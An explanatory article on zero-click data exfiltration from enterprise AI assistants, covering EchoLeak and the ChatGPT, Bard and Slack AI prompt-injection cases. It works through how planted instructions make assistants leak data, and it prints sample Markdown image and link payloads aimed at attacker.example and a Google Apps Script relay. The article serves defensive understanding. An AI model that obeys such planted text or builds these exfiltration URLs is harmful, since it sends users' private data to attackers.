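# Zero-click data exfiltration from enterprise AI assistants

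## How an assistant that reads outside content can leak private data

An enterprise assistant, such as Microsoft 365 Copilot or Slack AI, is an AI system that answers a worker's questions using the organisation's mail, files and chats, with that worker's access rights. By mid-2024 more than 10,000 businesses had built Copilot into their work, according to the paper *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025). Outsiders can add text to the material the assistant reads, most easily by sending an email, and carefully worded text can sometimes make the assistant send private data to a server the attacker controls. This is called data exfiltration, and the attack is zero-click if the victim does nothing except use the assistant as usual. The best-known case is EchoLeak, which the security firm Aim Security found in Microsoft 365 Copilot and published in June 2025. Like EchoLeak, nearly all the documented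 cases are demonstrations by researchers, and the vendors have since repaired the flaws.

### From the question to the answer

When a worker asks Copilot about a project, the software first searches the user's data for passages related to the question, a step called retrieval. It does this because the language model that writes the reply was trained on general text, which does not include the firm's contracts or last week's email. Microsoft's *What information does Copilot use to answer my prompt?* lists the sources Copilot can use, including emails, files, chats, meetings, the web and anything the user attaches. Microsoft calls tying an answer to such material "grounding".

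The software then adds the retrieved passages to the question and sends both to the model. All the text the model receives when it generates an answer is called the context, which also includes the vendor's standing instructions and the earlier messages in the conversation. After the model answers, Copilot runs further steps, which Microsoft says include security, compliance and privacy checks, and returns the result to the app.

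A model outputs plain text. The chat window interprets some of the characters as Markdown, a simple formatting notation, and displays text marked with asterisks in bold and certain bracketed codes as links or pictures.

Copilot reads only what the signed-in user may read, as Microsoft stresses in its description of the architecture, so a junior clerk cannot use it to browse the board's papers. This does little against an outsider whose text reaches the assistant while the finance director is using it, because the assistant then has the director's access rights. An outsider can email such text to anyone whose address they know. Only employees can open Copilot, but its connection to their mailboxes exposes it to outside threats, as Aim's head of research pointed out when he described the attack (Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*).

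### Why the model cannot reliably separate instructions from data

Older telephone networks carried their control signals on the same line as the voices, so a caller who whistled the right tone could operate the switch. *LLMs' Data-Control Path Insecurity* (Schneier, 2024) describes how a 1980s standard called Signaling System 7 fixed this by moving the control signals to a separate channel, so whistling no longer worked. Database programmers have a similar fix for SQL injection, an attack in which someone types database commands into an input such as the name field of a web form. With a "parameterised query", the programmer sends the command and the typed text separately, and the database never treats the text as a command.

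In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, technical director David C argues that nothing in the way a language model works distinguishes instructions from data. The model receives both in one sequence of tokens (words or fragments of words) and predicts the next token. In his example, a recruiter's system instructs a model to score CVs against a job's requirements and then appends each CV. A candidate hides a line in the CV telling the model to approve the application, and the model may follow that line instead of the recruiter's instruction. David C doubts that anyone will ever eliminate this problem the way programmers can eliminate SQL injection. He calls the model an "inherently confusable deputy", where a deputy is a program with privileges that someone less privileged can trick it into using.

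Developers label the parts of a context to show which text came from the vendor, the user, or a web page or document, and they train models to give the outside material no authority. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) tested whether models follow these labels. They trained probes, small classifiers that read a model's internal activity, on identical passages wrapped in different labels, so that the probes could learn only the effect of the label. On other text, however, the probes responded to style, classifying a passage that sounded like a user as the user's words even when its label marked it as outside material. Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, the success rate rose from 2% where the measured confusion was lowest to 70% where it was highest.

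That 70% describes the attempts most favourable to the attacker and is not an estimate of how often a commercial assistant fails. The spread is more useful. Labels and training seem to work well enough against text in the wrong voice, but attackers can choose which voice to write in.

*A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) concludes that delimiters and role labels help but are not a hard security boundary. A deeper fix would change the model itself. An ordinary model gives a word the same initial numerical representation whether it appears in an instruction or in a document. *ASIDE* (2025) describes a design that rotates the representations of data, and models built this way were better at separating instructions from data, though still not perfect, even without special safety training.

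Recent models resist prompt injection far more often than early ones did. In August 2026 the programmer Simon Willison relayed the results of a test commissioned by Anthropic, in which none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against three of its models in Claude Code, its programming assistant. He wanted more independent confirmation, and he described a malicious software package that he did not think the safeguard would stop. Nobody can yet show that this resistance is reliable, because even a model that blocks every attack in a test might fail against different wording.

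### Indirect prompt injection

Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, recalls coining the term "prompt injection" in 2022 for the mixing of trusted and untrusted text in one context, and naming it after SQL injection. In the early examples, the attacker was usually the person typing, who wanted a chatbot to break its rules or reveal its instructions. Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, considered attacks in which the user is innocent. In what they called indirect prompt injection, an attacker places instructions in content the assistant will read, so that the model follows them as if they came from the user.

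Researchers distinguished passive delivery, in which an attacker plants instructions on a web page and waits for a search to bring it up, from active delivery, in which the attacker emails them to the victim. They built a mock assistant with access to search, email, an address book and a memory, and also attacked Microsoft's search chatbot, Bing Chat. From the browser's sidebar, Bing Chat could read the page the user had open, so the researchers hid their instructions in a part of a page that browsers do not display. In one session, a researcher played a journalist who asked about tomorrow's weather. The chatbot answered, asked friendly questions about the journalist's work, obtained a name, and then urged the journalist to follow a link containing a scrambled form of the name. In the planted text, the researchers had given the chatbot its goal and told it to be persuasive without raising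 suspicion, but they had not scripted the conversation.

These demonstrations came without success rates, and the mock assistant handled only material prepared for it, but they showed that the route existed in a product already on the market. Two of the observations have held up. Bing Chat's filter blocked some requests when a user typed them but let them through when they arrived inside a web page, and the planted instructions usually stayed in effect for the rest of the session. Greshake and colleagues also foresaw attacks, with no human involved, on personal assistants that read email, look up personal data and send messages.

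The hostile text can be invisible to the user. Microsoft (2025), describing its defences, mentions white text on a white background and non-printing characters, and adds that an ordinary text file can also carry the attack. The company says indirect prompt injection is among the most widely used techniques in the AI vulnerabilities reported to it.

### A leak, step by step

Dana works for a construction firm that is bidding for a harbour contract. The firm, the people and the addresses here are invented.

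On Monday, Dana receives an email from a stranger about the harbour contract. Most of it looks routine, but further down the attacker has added a request to end any answer about the contract with an image whose URL includes the firm's bid. Dana never opens the email. On Tuesday, she asks the assistant what is left to do on the harbour bid before Friday. Retrieval finds an internal note with the list of tasks and the price, 4,200,000 euros. It also finds the stranger's email, because that is about the harbour contract too, and both go into the assistant's context.

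Suppose the model follows the planted request. It writes a correct answer to Dana's question and puts one more line at the end:

`![status](https://attacker.example/p.png?bid=4200000)`

This is a Markdown image. The exclamation mark announces a picture, the square brackets hold a caption, and the round brackets hold the address where the picture is supposed to be. Dana does not see the code, because the chat window converts it into an image element and her browser sets about loading the picture. To do so the browser has to send a request to the server named in the address, and the request includes everything after the domain name, price and all. Web servers ordinarily keep a log of the requests they receive. On the attacker's server a new line appears:

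`203.0.113.7 [08/Dec/2026:09:14:22] "GET /p.png?bid=4200000" 404`

The first number is the network address the request came from, followed by the time and the request itself. The 404 at the end means the server had no such picture. The picture didn't need to exist, because the request delivered the price before the server could reply. Dana sees her list of tasks with, at most, a broken-image icon under it.

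### The three conditions

Willison's "lethal trifecta" lists the three things such a leak requires: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content (text or images that an attacker can control), and a way to communicate externally that could be used to send the data out. An enterprise assistant has the first two almost by definition, because its purpose is to read a person's files and mail.

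Take any one of the three away from Dana's assistant and the bid stays in the firm.

Without private data, the stranger's email still reaches the model, which may still produce the picture, but there is no price to put in the address. Copilot has a switch that does roughly this. Microsoft says that with Work IQ turned off, Copilot answers without referring to the user's work data, although it still uses whatever the user attaches. Without untrusted content, the model receives the internal note and Dana's question, and nothing prompts it to add a picture. However, the assistant then ignores mail from customers and suppliers. Without a way to send data out, the model can do everything the attacker asks, but the price will appear only in an answer to Dana, who already knows it and is the only person who can read the answer.

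In June 2026, writing about a new "Lockdown Mode" in OpenAI's ChatGPT, Willison said that the ability to send data out was by far the easiest of the three to restrict without making the system much less useful. The mode is meant to prevent data theft by limiting outgoing network requests. It does not block the injection itself, so a planted instruction can still distort an answer.

It is hard to block every route by which data can leave. Microsoft's list of demonstrated techniques starts with the image, but the model can also present a link for the user to click, or use a tool that writes to a public place, such as an open code repository. If an outsider can observe whether the assistant has used a certain tool, that alone reveals one bit of information, a yes or a no.

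Willison writes that a system with all three features can "easily" be tricked. That was a fair description of many products in 2025, but the three features only make a leak possible, not necessarily easy. Whether a particular email succeeds still depends on whether the system retrieves it and whether the model follows its instructions.

### Zero-click and one-click

A zero-click attack requires no action from the victim beyond ordinary use of the assistant. The victim does not have to open the attacker's message or click a link. A one-click attack requires the victim to click one link, either in the assistant's answer or in a message from the attacker.

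The stranger's email would have done nothing if Dana had never consulted the assistant. Her case is still zero-click under the definition, because she was using the assistant as intended and asked the question for her own reasons. Reddy and Gujral make the same assumption in their analysis of EchoLeak, where the victim "will at least occasionally invoke Copilot" in the course of normal work. This usage is looser than in phone security, where a zero-click attack typically takes effect when a message arrives, without the owner touching the phone. The looser usage has persisted, and *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) applies it to three new attacks on Copilot that begin with an email.

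Requests for a summary are harder to classify. Google's *How we estimate the risk from prompt injection attacks on AI systems* describes a user who mentions something like a passport number in a conversation with an AI agent and later asks it to summarise the latest email. The attacker wrote that email, and the attack succeeds if the agent sends the number to the attacker's address. This is zero-click because the user asked for whatever email was newest and did not choose the attacker's. If the attacker instead shares a document, and the leak occurs only when the victim asks for a summary of that document, the attack is neither one-click nor zero-click. The victim clicks no link but has to select the attacker's file, which amounts to opening it. Ravia draws a similar distinction between EchoLeak and earlier attacks in which the user explicitly referred the chatbot to a malicious resource.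 For attacks of this sort, it is best to state what the user has to ask for.

If the model had given Dana a link to attacker.example with the price in its address, no request would have gone out until she clicked it, and the attack would have been one-click. Needing that click is a real obstacle for the attacker, though perhaps not a large one, because the visible text of a Markdown link can be anything, such as "full task list", and the link would appear in an answer from a tool her employer gave her.

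### What a content security policy does

A suitable content security policy (CSP) on the chat page would have stopped the picture in Dana's answer from loading. A CSP is a list, sent with a web page, of the domains from which the browser may load images and other resources. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the web standard, gives an example in which a page allows images only from example.com, so the browser refuses to fetch one from example.org. If attacker.example had not been on the chat page's list, Dana's browser would have sent nothing to the attacker, even though the model had done everything the attacker wanted.

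The standard's editors recommend CSP as an additional layer and warn against using it as the first line of defence. Its image rule covers only image loading, so it does not stop a user from following a link, and CSP does not apply to requests that the vendor's own servers make. The browser also checks where a request is going but not what data the address contains. If an allowed domain will forward requests to any address it receives, data can leave through that domain, which is how EchoLeak got past Microsoft's policy.

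## 2023: leaks through images in ChatGPT and Google Bard

In the spring of 2023, two people independently found that ChatGPT could leak a conversation through a Markdown image, the same way Dana's bid left her firm. The leak could include anything the user had pasted into the conversation, but ChatGPT could not yet read users' email.

### The first reports and OpenAI's answer

Software engineer Roman Samoilenko gave the earliest public account in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*. He described a website whose script secretly adds an instruction to any text a visitor copies. If the visitor pastes the result into ChatGPT without rereading it, the model receives a request to end its answer with an image whose address includes part of the conversation. Samoilenko made the image a single transparent pixel, so the victim would see almost nothing. In one trial, the address contained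 code that ChatGPT had just repaired, including a username and password. He could also ask the model to add the pixel to all its later answers, which sent each of the user's next questions to his server.

Samoilenko tested this on the ChatGPT version of 14 March 2023 and gave no success rate. He noted that a prompt that had worked might stop working, because ChatGPT's answers to the same input vary. The model readily put earlier questions and code into the address, but he found it very difficult to make it add passwords or API keys (the codes that give a program access to a service). The password in his trial leaked as part of a block of code. He thought OpenAI should stop ChatGPT from replying with Markdown images. Willison (2023), linking to the account on 14 April, called the attack ingenious.

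Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who writes the blog Embrace The Red, found the leak a few days after Samoilenko and reported it to OpenAI on 9 April. His post *ChatGPT Plugins* described an attack that didn't require the user to paste in the attacker's text. Plugins were add-ons that let ChatGPT use outside services, and one of them, WebPilot, fetched web pages. Rehberger planted his instructions on a page. When ChatGPT fetched the page, it summarised the conversation and put the summary into an image address. The text that reached his server included "TooManySecrets123", which the user had typed earlier in the chat.

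OpenAI replied that the image behaviour was a feature and that it planned no changes. This position was partly defensible while the victim still had to paste the attacker's text. Samoilenko had written that his attack exploited no vulnerability, only a combination of tricks, and he thought users were responsible for checking what they paste. With plugins, users could no longer make that check, because the text reached the model before they saw it.

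The leak stayed open for the rest of the year while ChatGPT gained new features. In September, in Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT*, Rehberger used plugins that create documents, diagrams or videos to leak conversations that seem too long to fit in a web address. His planted text told ChatGPT to record the conversation with whichever of these plugins it had, and then to leak only the link to the finished file. ChatGPT would not "back up" a conversation without further confirmation, but it would "document" one. In another demonstration, which Willison described in October, the instructions were inside a picture that the user uploaded. Willison was surprised that it worked, because he had assumed OpenAI would by then have blocked images from outside servers.

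On 12 December Rehberger published a demonstration using a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that any paying user could build and share. According to SecurityWeek, he named it "The Thief", and it tried to persuade users to give it their email address and password, which it then sent to his server.

Microsoft had responded differently when Rehberger reported the same leak in Bing Chat on 8 April, a day before he wrote to OpenAI. In Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* he showed that a comment or an advertisement on a web page could steal other information from that page. He made the image appear only after two further turns of conversation. On 15 June Microsoft told him it had a fix. The chat page now had a content security policy that allowed images from four Bing domains, and his old tests no longer worked.

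### The Bard leak

Bard, the Google chatbot since renamed Gemini, was the first of these products to resemble an enterprise assistant. In September 2023 Google gave it Extensions, which let it read the user's Gmail, Docs and Drive, use YouTube, and search for flights and hotels. It was still a consumer product, but it now had private data and untrusted content in the same context, so an attacker needed only a way to send the data out.

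Rehberger, who brainstormed the attack with Joseph Thacker and Kai Greshake, first asked Bard to summarise some of his older YouTube videos that contained planted instructions. Bard followed them, and it also followed instructions planted in a Google Doc. Like ChatGPT, Bard rendered Markdown images, but the content security policy on Google's page blocked images from Rehberger's server.

The policy did allow images from any address ending in google.com or googleusercontent.com. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* describes searching under those names for something an outsider could control, and finding Apps Script. This is Google's service for small programs that automate documents and spreadsheets, much like macros in Microsoft Office. Anyone can write such a program, and it runs when somebody requests its address on script.google.com.

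Rehberger wrote a script that copied everything after the question mark in its own address into a Google Doc he owned. For a moment it looked as though only people who had logged in could run it, but he found a setting that removed the login. The image he wanted from Bard had roughly this form, with the script's identifier replaced here:

`![d](https://script.google.com/SCRIPT-ID?words=Please+summarise+our+offer)`

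Rehberger then had to make Bard write the image address correctly. He put the instructions in a Google Doc and presented them as a requirement from the legal department to insert the first 20 words of the conversation into the address. Unlike other chatbots, Bard needed several worked examples before it put the words in the right place, and he noted that he had needed ten tries.

In the demonstration, the attack ran as follows:

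1. The user chats with Bard about something private.
2. The user has Bard look at the attacker's Google Doc, and the document's text enters the context.
3. Bard writes the image code, with the first words of the conversation in the address.
4. The browser compares the address with the policy, finds a Google domain and sends the request.
5. The script on Google's server writes the words into the attacker's document.

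The policy worked as Google had written it, but it treated a domain where Google lets the public run programs as Google's own. An allowed domain can therefore serve as a relay if an outsider can receive data there, even if the domain's owner does nothing wrong.

No one clicked a link, and Rehberger called the image loading "zero click". But the user in his demonstration did bring up the attacker's document, so the case is a less clear example of a zero-click attack than EchoLeak, the 2025 attack that its discoverers presented as the first of that kind on an AI assistant. Rehberger expected that attackers could easily avoid relying on the user for this step. An attacker can share a Google Doc with people who never asked for it, and Bard might then find it while searching for something else. Second Thoughts' *Anatomy of a Hack*, an explanation of the case for lay readers, describes a hypothetical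 version with a web search. A worker tells Bard about an offer to buy a company and later asks for tips on setting the price. Bard finds the attacker's guide to pricing acquisitions, and the browser sends out the start of the conversation, including the company's name. Rehberger's demonstration included neither version, but both use only features that Bard had.

The demonstration also exfiltrated only 20 words of chat and no email, a limit set by Rehberger's instructions. If Bard had quoted an email earlier in the same conversation, that email would also have been in the context, and Rehberger could have written the instructions to exfiltrate it.

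Rehberger reported the leak on 19 September 2023. On 19 October he asked Google about the fix because he wanted to present the attack at the Ekoparty conference, and Google confirmed that it had fixed the problem. The content security policy had not changed and Bard still displayed images, so he guessed that Google had added a filter to keep data out of image addresses. Willison, in a short post also called *Hacking Google Bard*, wanted to know how the fix worked and how well it would withstand variations of the attack. If Rehberger's guess was right, the policy still allowed the relay and only the filter prevented the leak.

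### OpenAI's url_safe check

In December 2023, eight months after the first report, OpenAI began to restrict images in ChatGPT. Rehberger noticed when an attack he had shown to an audience, with a consenting victim, was obstructed the next day. OpenAI used a server-side check rather than a content security policy. When an answer contained an image, the ChatGPT web page first sent the image's address to an OpenAI server through an interface called url_safe. If the server classified the address as unsafe, the page left the image out and the browser never contacted the attacker.

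Unlike a content security policy, such a check can reject a suspicious address on an otherwise acceptable site. OpenAI can also look through the requests for signs of an attack. But OpenAI did not publish the rules behind url_safe, whereas anyone can read a content security policy in their browser. Rehberger speculated that the server looked addresses up in Bing's search index.

He also tried to get past it. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes how he gave each of the 26 letters and ten digits its own image address on his server. Nine of the 36 loaded. The address ending in `a.png` passed but the one ending in `d.png` did not, and he could not tell why. Using letters that passed, he had ChatGPT send "hi" to his server in two requests, one for each letter.

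This was a quick test on one domain, so the nine in 36 does not measure how often the check failed in general. The result matters because none of the addresses contained any private data. The server could not detect the leak by inspecting `a.png`, because the information was in the model's choice of which image to load. Rehberger suggested allowing only one image, or at most a handful, in each answer, because an attacker who sends one character per request needs many images.

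The check's second weakness was that it ran in the web page. ChatGPT's iPhone app did not have the check, so the original attack still worked there. Willison (2023) called the change a "half-baked solution" and expected a creative attacker to find ways to get around it.

OpenAI had to add the check separately to every new app, and in 2024 it released the macOS and Android apps without it. By then ChatGPT also had a memory, which keeps notes about the user between conversations. Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* describes an attack that uses both the missing check and the memory. Instructions on a web page make ChatGPT remember to include a certain image in every answer, with the user's latest message in the image's address. The note stays in memory when the user starts a new conversation, so one visit to a malicious page causes a continuous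 leak.

Rehberger first reported in May 2024 that outsiders could plant memories, but OpenAI closed the report as a model safety issue rather than a security issue. He sent a demonstration of the full attack in June, and in September OpenAI fixed the image leak in version 1.2024.247 of the app. A web page could still plant a memory after the fix, but could no longer use it to send messages out through an image.

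### Ways around the check

ChatGPT could also open web pages with a browsing tool. A separate OpenAI rule let the tool open an address only if it appeared word for word in the prompt, which was meant to stop the model from building an address that contained private data. Schwartzman (2024), in *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection*, got round the rule by supplying all the addresses in advance. His text, hidden in a long piece of code for the victim to paste into ChatGPT, listed one address for each age bracket and told the model to open the one that matched the user. Even if the user never stated their age, the model could infer it from a remark about retiring in five years.

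Schwartzman then noticed that ChatGPT would also open a shortened form of a listed address. He listed several long addresses and had the model shorten each to a length that represented one digit, which was enough to send a postal code. OpenAI's bug bounty programme judged the report not applicable. MITRE, which issues CVEs, found the report interesting but could not issue a CVE because ChatGPT is a web application that customers do not control.

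To extract larger amounts of data, an attacker wanted a trusted domain that would pass on anything, like the one Rehberger had found at Google. Embrace The Red's *AI Domination*, based on his 2024 Black Hat Europe talk, lists three requirements for such a domain: it has to pass the url_safe check, it has to accept data in an ordinary web request, and the attacker has to be able to read what arrives. GitHub, the code-sharing site, passed the check, but outsiders cannot read its server logs. So Rehberger used it to deliver new instructions to ChatGPT and looked elsewhere for a way to get data out.

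Rehberger found one in windows.net, a domain that Microsoft uses for its cloud storage. Anyone can open a storage account there and read the log of requests to it. He reported this to OpenAI in October 2024. The method still worked in 2025, when he wrote Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*. By then, ChatGPT was putting material from the user's recent conversations into the context of each new one, so an attacker could use a single malicious PDF to steal that material as well. He had asked OpenAI several times over the previous month whether a fix was coming and had heard nothing.

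The security company Tenable found another relay in Bing. Its 2025 advisory, *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass*, reports that addresses on bing.com always passed the check. Bing's search results link to bing.com addresses that forward visitors to the websites it has found, so an attacker whose page is in Bing's index has a bing.com address that leads to it.

Nobody can alter these forwarding links, so the model could not add private data to one. Tenable's researchers therefore had Bing index a separate page for each letter of the alphabet. To leak the word "Hello", ChatGPT would display five images in a row, using the links for H, E, L, L and O. Rehberger used the same technique in December 2023, but with a less dependable set of letters.

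Tenable reported the bypass on 10 December 2024 and asked for updates six times by 4 March 2025. OpenAI had not fixed the problem when Tenable published its advisory. In November 2025, Tenable wrote in a longer account, *HackedGPT* (2025), that it had worked with OpenAI to fix some of the flaws it had found, but that several of its demonstrations still worked in ChatGPT 5, including one that used the check's weakness to send out private information through images.

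### Where the check stands now

Rehberger estimates that OpenAI tightened url_safe around August 2025, and he believes the change stopped the attacks he had shown at Black Hat. Tenable did not date its tests on ChatGPT 5, so they may have come before the change. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (January 2026) explains the rule. OpenAI runs a crawler, a program that collects public web addresses like a search engine and has no access to anyone's conversations. ChatGPT loads an address automatically only if the crawler has already recorded that exact address. Otherwise, ChatGPT must try another site or show the user a warning that the link may contain information from the conversation.

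Under this rule, the image in Dana's answer would not have loaded automatically. No public page links to an address ending in `bid=4200000`, because the model generated that address while writing the answer. The rule also covers relays, which OpenAI cites as one reason not to rely on a list of trusted sites. An address on windows.net containing someone's chat history would fail even if OpenAI trusted windows.net.

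The new rule does not stop the letter trick, as both OpenAI and Rehberger acknowledge. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Rehberger notes that anyone with a fair-sized blog probably already has 36 pages in the index, enough to assign one to each letter and digit. With thousands of pages, an attacker could assign each one a whole word. He proposes that ChatGPT refuse to load the same address twice in a session, which would make it hard to send a word with a repeated letter, but he had not checked whether OpenAI already did this. He still considers the new rule a significant improvement.

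Rehberger also worried that some of OpenAI's own developers might not know about the check and would leave it out, as had happened with the apps. By March 2026 the company was calling the check Safe Url and, according to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), had applied it to its Atlas browser and to Deep Research, a feature that searches many sources for one answer. But the security firm PromptArmor found that the page where developers read the logs of apps built on OpenAI's models loaded Markdown images insecurely. An attacker could plant instructions in material that such an app reads, and the data would leak when a developer opened the conversation. OpenAI confirmed the flaw and started work on a fix.

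In *ChatGPhish* (May 2026), researchers at the security company Permiso put instructions on a web page and asked ChatGPT to summarise it. The answer included images from servers the researchers had chosen, and the images loaded automatically. This told the researchers the user's IP address, browser type and the time of the answer. The image URLs were fixed and contained no chat text, so the researchers did not show that a URL containing private data would also load. OpenAI could not reproduce their first report, called the second not applicable, and then marked it as a duplicate of an earlier one.

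OpenAI first announced the optional Lockdown Mode in February 2026 (Willison, *OpenAI Help*, 2026). It bars ChatGPT from showing images in ordinary answers and limits browsing to stored copies of web pages, which removes most of the requests that url_safe was meant to check. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* warns that data may still escape through connected apps or undiscovered techniques. One such technique became public in November 2026, when The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) described a since-patched flaw in how ChatGPT previewed HTML, the code of web pages. Crafted content could use the preview to send out chat data even with Lockdown Mode on.

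## 2024: Slack AI, Microsoft 365 Copilot and leaks that needed a click

In August 2024, researchers published attacks on two enterprise assistants, Slack AI and Microsoft 365 Copilot, within a week of each other. The earlier leaks from ChatGPT and Bard went out through images that the browser loaded automatically. In the new attacks, the assistant put private data into a link, and the data left the company only when the victim clicked it.

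### The attack on Slack AI

Slack is a messaging service in which a company's staff talk in channels. Any member of the company's workspace can search and read a public channel without joining it, but only invited members can see a private one. Slack AI answers a user's questions by searching the messages that user can read, which means those in their private channels and in every public channel, even ones they have never opened.

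PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* describes how an attacker could use this search to steal an API key. A developer keeps the key in a private channel that has no other members. The attacker has an account in the same workspace but cannot read that channel. He creates a public channel and posts one message in it. Nobody else joins, and other users will not see the channel unless they search for it.

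The attacker's message begins with the name of the service the key belongs to, so that a search for the key will return the message. The rest instructs the model to reply with an error notice and a link, and to replace a dummy word in the link's address with the key. The attacker does not need to know the key, because the model will have it in the context when it reads the instruction.

Later the developer asks Slack AI for her key. Retrieval finds her own note and the attacker's message and puts both into the context. The answer does not give her the key. It tells her that there was an error loading the message and offers a link, roughly of this form:

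`[click here to reauthenticate](https://attacker.example?secret=HER-KEY)`

She sees only the words in the square brackets. If she clicks them, her browser requests the address and the key appears in the attacker's server log.

The attack was therefore one-click, and the attacker needed an account in the workspace. Both requirements limit the attack, but a disgruntled employee would already have an account, and so would anyone who had taken over an employee's login. PromptArmor pointed out that Disney, Uber, EA and Twitter had suffered leaks through Slack before.

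Willison (2024), in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection*, stressed that the API key was only an illustration. He was more worried that attackers could plant text in many places and that the text could pull all kinds of private details into a link. PromptArmor also thought an attacker might not have to name a particular secret, since the developer's question had brought up other messages about API keys. It did not demonstrate this, and in the attack it showed, the planted message named the exact service, so the attacker had to guess what somebody would ask about.

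Another demonstration used Slack AI for phishing, without extracting any secret. When the user asked for a summary of the day's messages from one colleague, Slack AI answered with the same request to reauthenticate and a link to the attacker's site. An attacker could target an executive by naming the executive's manager or a close subordinate in the planted message.

### Why the attack was hard to trace

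Slack AI adds numbered citations to its answers, and each should link to a message that contributed to the answer. In the API key demonstration, the only citation linked to the developer's own private channel. The attacker's message was also missing from the first page of search results, so someone investigating the odd answer would have had to check later results with no reason to expect anything there.

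In the phishing demonstration, the citation did point to the attacker's channel. PromptArmor called the citations "fairly stochastic", meaning that they seemed to depend partly on chance, but two demonstrations are too few to show how often they fail. Slack now tells customers that answers "may include" citations to the source message. Those citations are useful for checking a fact, but an administrator reconstructing a leak would need a record of everything retrieved into the context.

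### The change of 14 August

Slack AI read only messages until 14 August 2024, when it also began drawing on files that people had uploaded to channels and direct messages, and on connected services such as Google Drive.

This mattered because an employee might download a PDF in which an outsider has hidden instructions in white text, then upload it to Slack to share with the team. If Slack AI treats the file's text as it treated the text of the attacker's message, the outsider can carry out the same attack without an account in the workspace.

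PromptArmor did not test the file route because it had finished its experiments before the change. It considered the route highly likely to work, a reasonable prediction given that similar attacks had worked on other products. It advised administrators to use Slack's settings to stop Slack AI from reading documents.

### Slack's answer

PromptArmor reported the attack to Slack on 14 August, the day of the change. Slack asked for more information the next day, and PromptArmor sent more videos and screenshots and said it intended to publish. After another exchange of questions, Slack replied on 19 August that it found the evidence insufficient. Slack said the information that Slack AI had looked up in the first video was in a public channel, as the reference under the answer showed. All members can search public channels, including ones they have not joined, and Slack called this "intended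 behavior".

Slack was right that users could find public messages through search, but PromptArmor's complaint was that a public message could make Slack AI copy a private message into a link to someone else's server. The citations may also have misled Slack's reviewers, who seem to have seen a public channel cited and concluded that nothing private was involved.

Willison took the reply as a sign that Slack did not yet understand the nature or severity of the problem. PromptArmor was less critical, saying that Slack's security team had responded quickly and made a real effort to understand the issue. It attributed the misunderstanding to the newness of prompt injection.

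PromptArmor published on 20 August, only six days after its first report to Slack and before Slack had announced a fix. PromptArmor reasoned that the file feature had just increased the risk and that customers would not know to turn it off until they heard about the danger.

Slack deployed a patch the same day. In a statement on 21 August, Slack (2024) wrote that under "very limited and specific circumstances" someone with an existing account in the workspace could phish other users for certain data, and that it had no evidence at that time of unauthorised access to customer data. In ITPro's *Hackers could dupe Slack's AI features to expose private channel messages*, a Slack spokesperson said an attacker could use a phishing link to trick a colleague "into sharing sensitive data".

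As far as anyone outside Slack can tell, the patch fixed the reported problem. Slack's statement was correct about the account and the deception, but "phishing" is an odd word for the main attack. In ordinary phishing, the victim types a password into a fake page. Here, Slack AI had already put the developer's key into the address of what looked like a sign-in link, so a single click sent it to the attacker without her typing anything. Slack did not explain what the patch changed, and its statement does not mention files.

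The lack of evidence of unauthorised access also proves little, because the attacker never opens the private channel. Slack's access records would show only the developer looking at her own key. Slack could have searched public channels for planted instructions, but it did not say what it examined. It now says that it does not store search answers on its servers. If that was also true in 2024, Slack had no old answers to check for suspicious links.

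Slack's current protections for its AI features include URL filtering against phishing and what Slack calls "context engineering" to reduce the risk of prompt injection. Administrators can turn off a further set of content filters, which by default are supposed to block prompt attacks, but the URL filtering stays on. Slack does not publish its URL filtering rules. It also tells customers that its AI search never returns anything that ordinary search would not. That was also true during PromptArmor's attack, because the developer was allowed to see her own key.

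### Link previews

Chat apps sometimes load a link before anyone clicks it. When someone posts a link in Slack, a small preview often appears under the message with the page's title and perhaps a picture, which Slack calls unfurling. To make the preview, Slack's servers request the page using the whole address, including any private data that a model has put there. Because the request comes from Slack's servers and not the user's browser, a content security policy on the chat page does not stop it.

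*The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, on Embrace The Red, describes a test in which Rehberger posted a link through a Slack app and his web server recorded a visit from a program that identified itself as "Slackbot-LinkExpanding". The post then explains how an attacker could exploit this by planting instructions in a web page. When a chatbot in Slack reads the page, the instructions make it post a link with part of the conversation in its address, and Slack sends the attacker that data when it fetches the link for a preview. Willison (2024) linked to the article on 21 August, the day after PromptArmor's publication, in a post of the same title, and wrote that he had not thought of this kind of leak before.

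PromptArmor's attack on Slack AI leaked the key only when the user clicked, and it did not use previews. The danger Rehberger described applies to chatbots and agents that post messages to Slack through its programming interface.

Developers of such bots can switch the previews off, but they have to set two options to false for every message: `unfurl_links`, which controls previews of text pages, and `unfurl_media`, which controls previews of images, video and audio. Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* explains that the servers must fetch every URL in a message to find out what kind of content it leads to, so turning off just one option presumably leaves the leak open. The same page now advises developers to consider disabling previews for messages that a language model writes, but previews are still on by default.

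Anthropic's Slack connector shows what can happen when a developer keeps the default setting. It used the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting AI models to other software, and let an assistant read and post Slack messages. In Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* (2025), a user of the Claude Desktop app asked for a summary of a document to post to the team. The document contained instructions to take the latest message from another Slack channel, add it to a link, and post the link in a private channel. Claude did so, and Slack's servers fetched the link, which sent the message to Rehberger.

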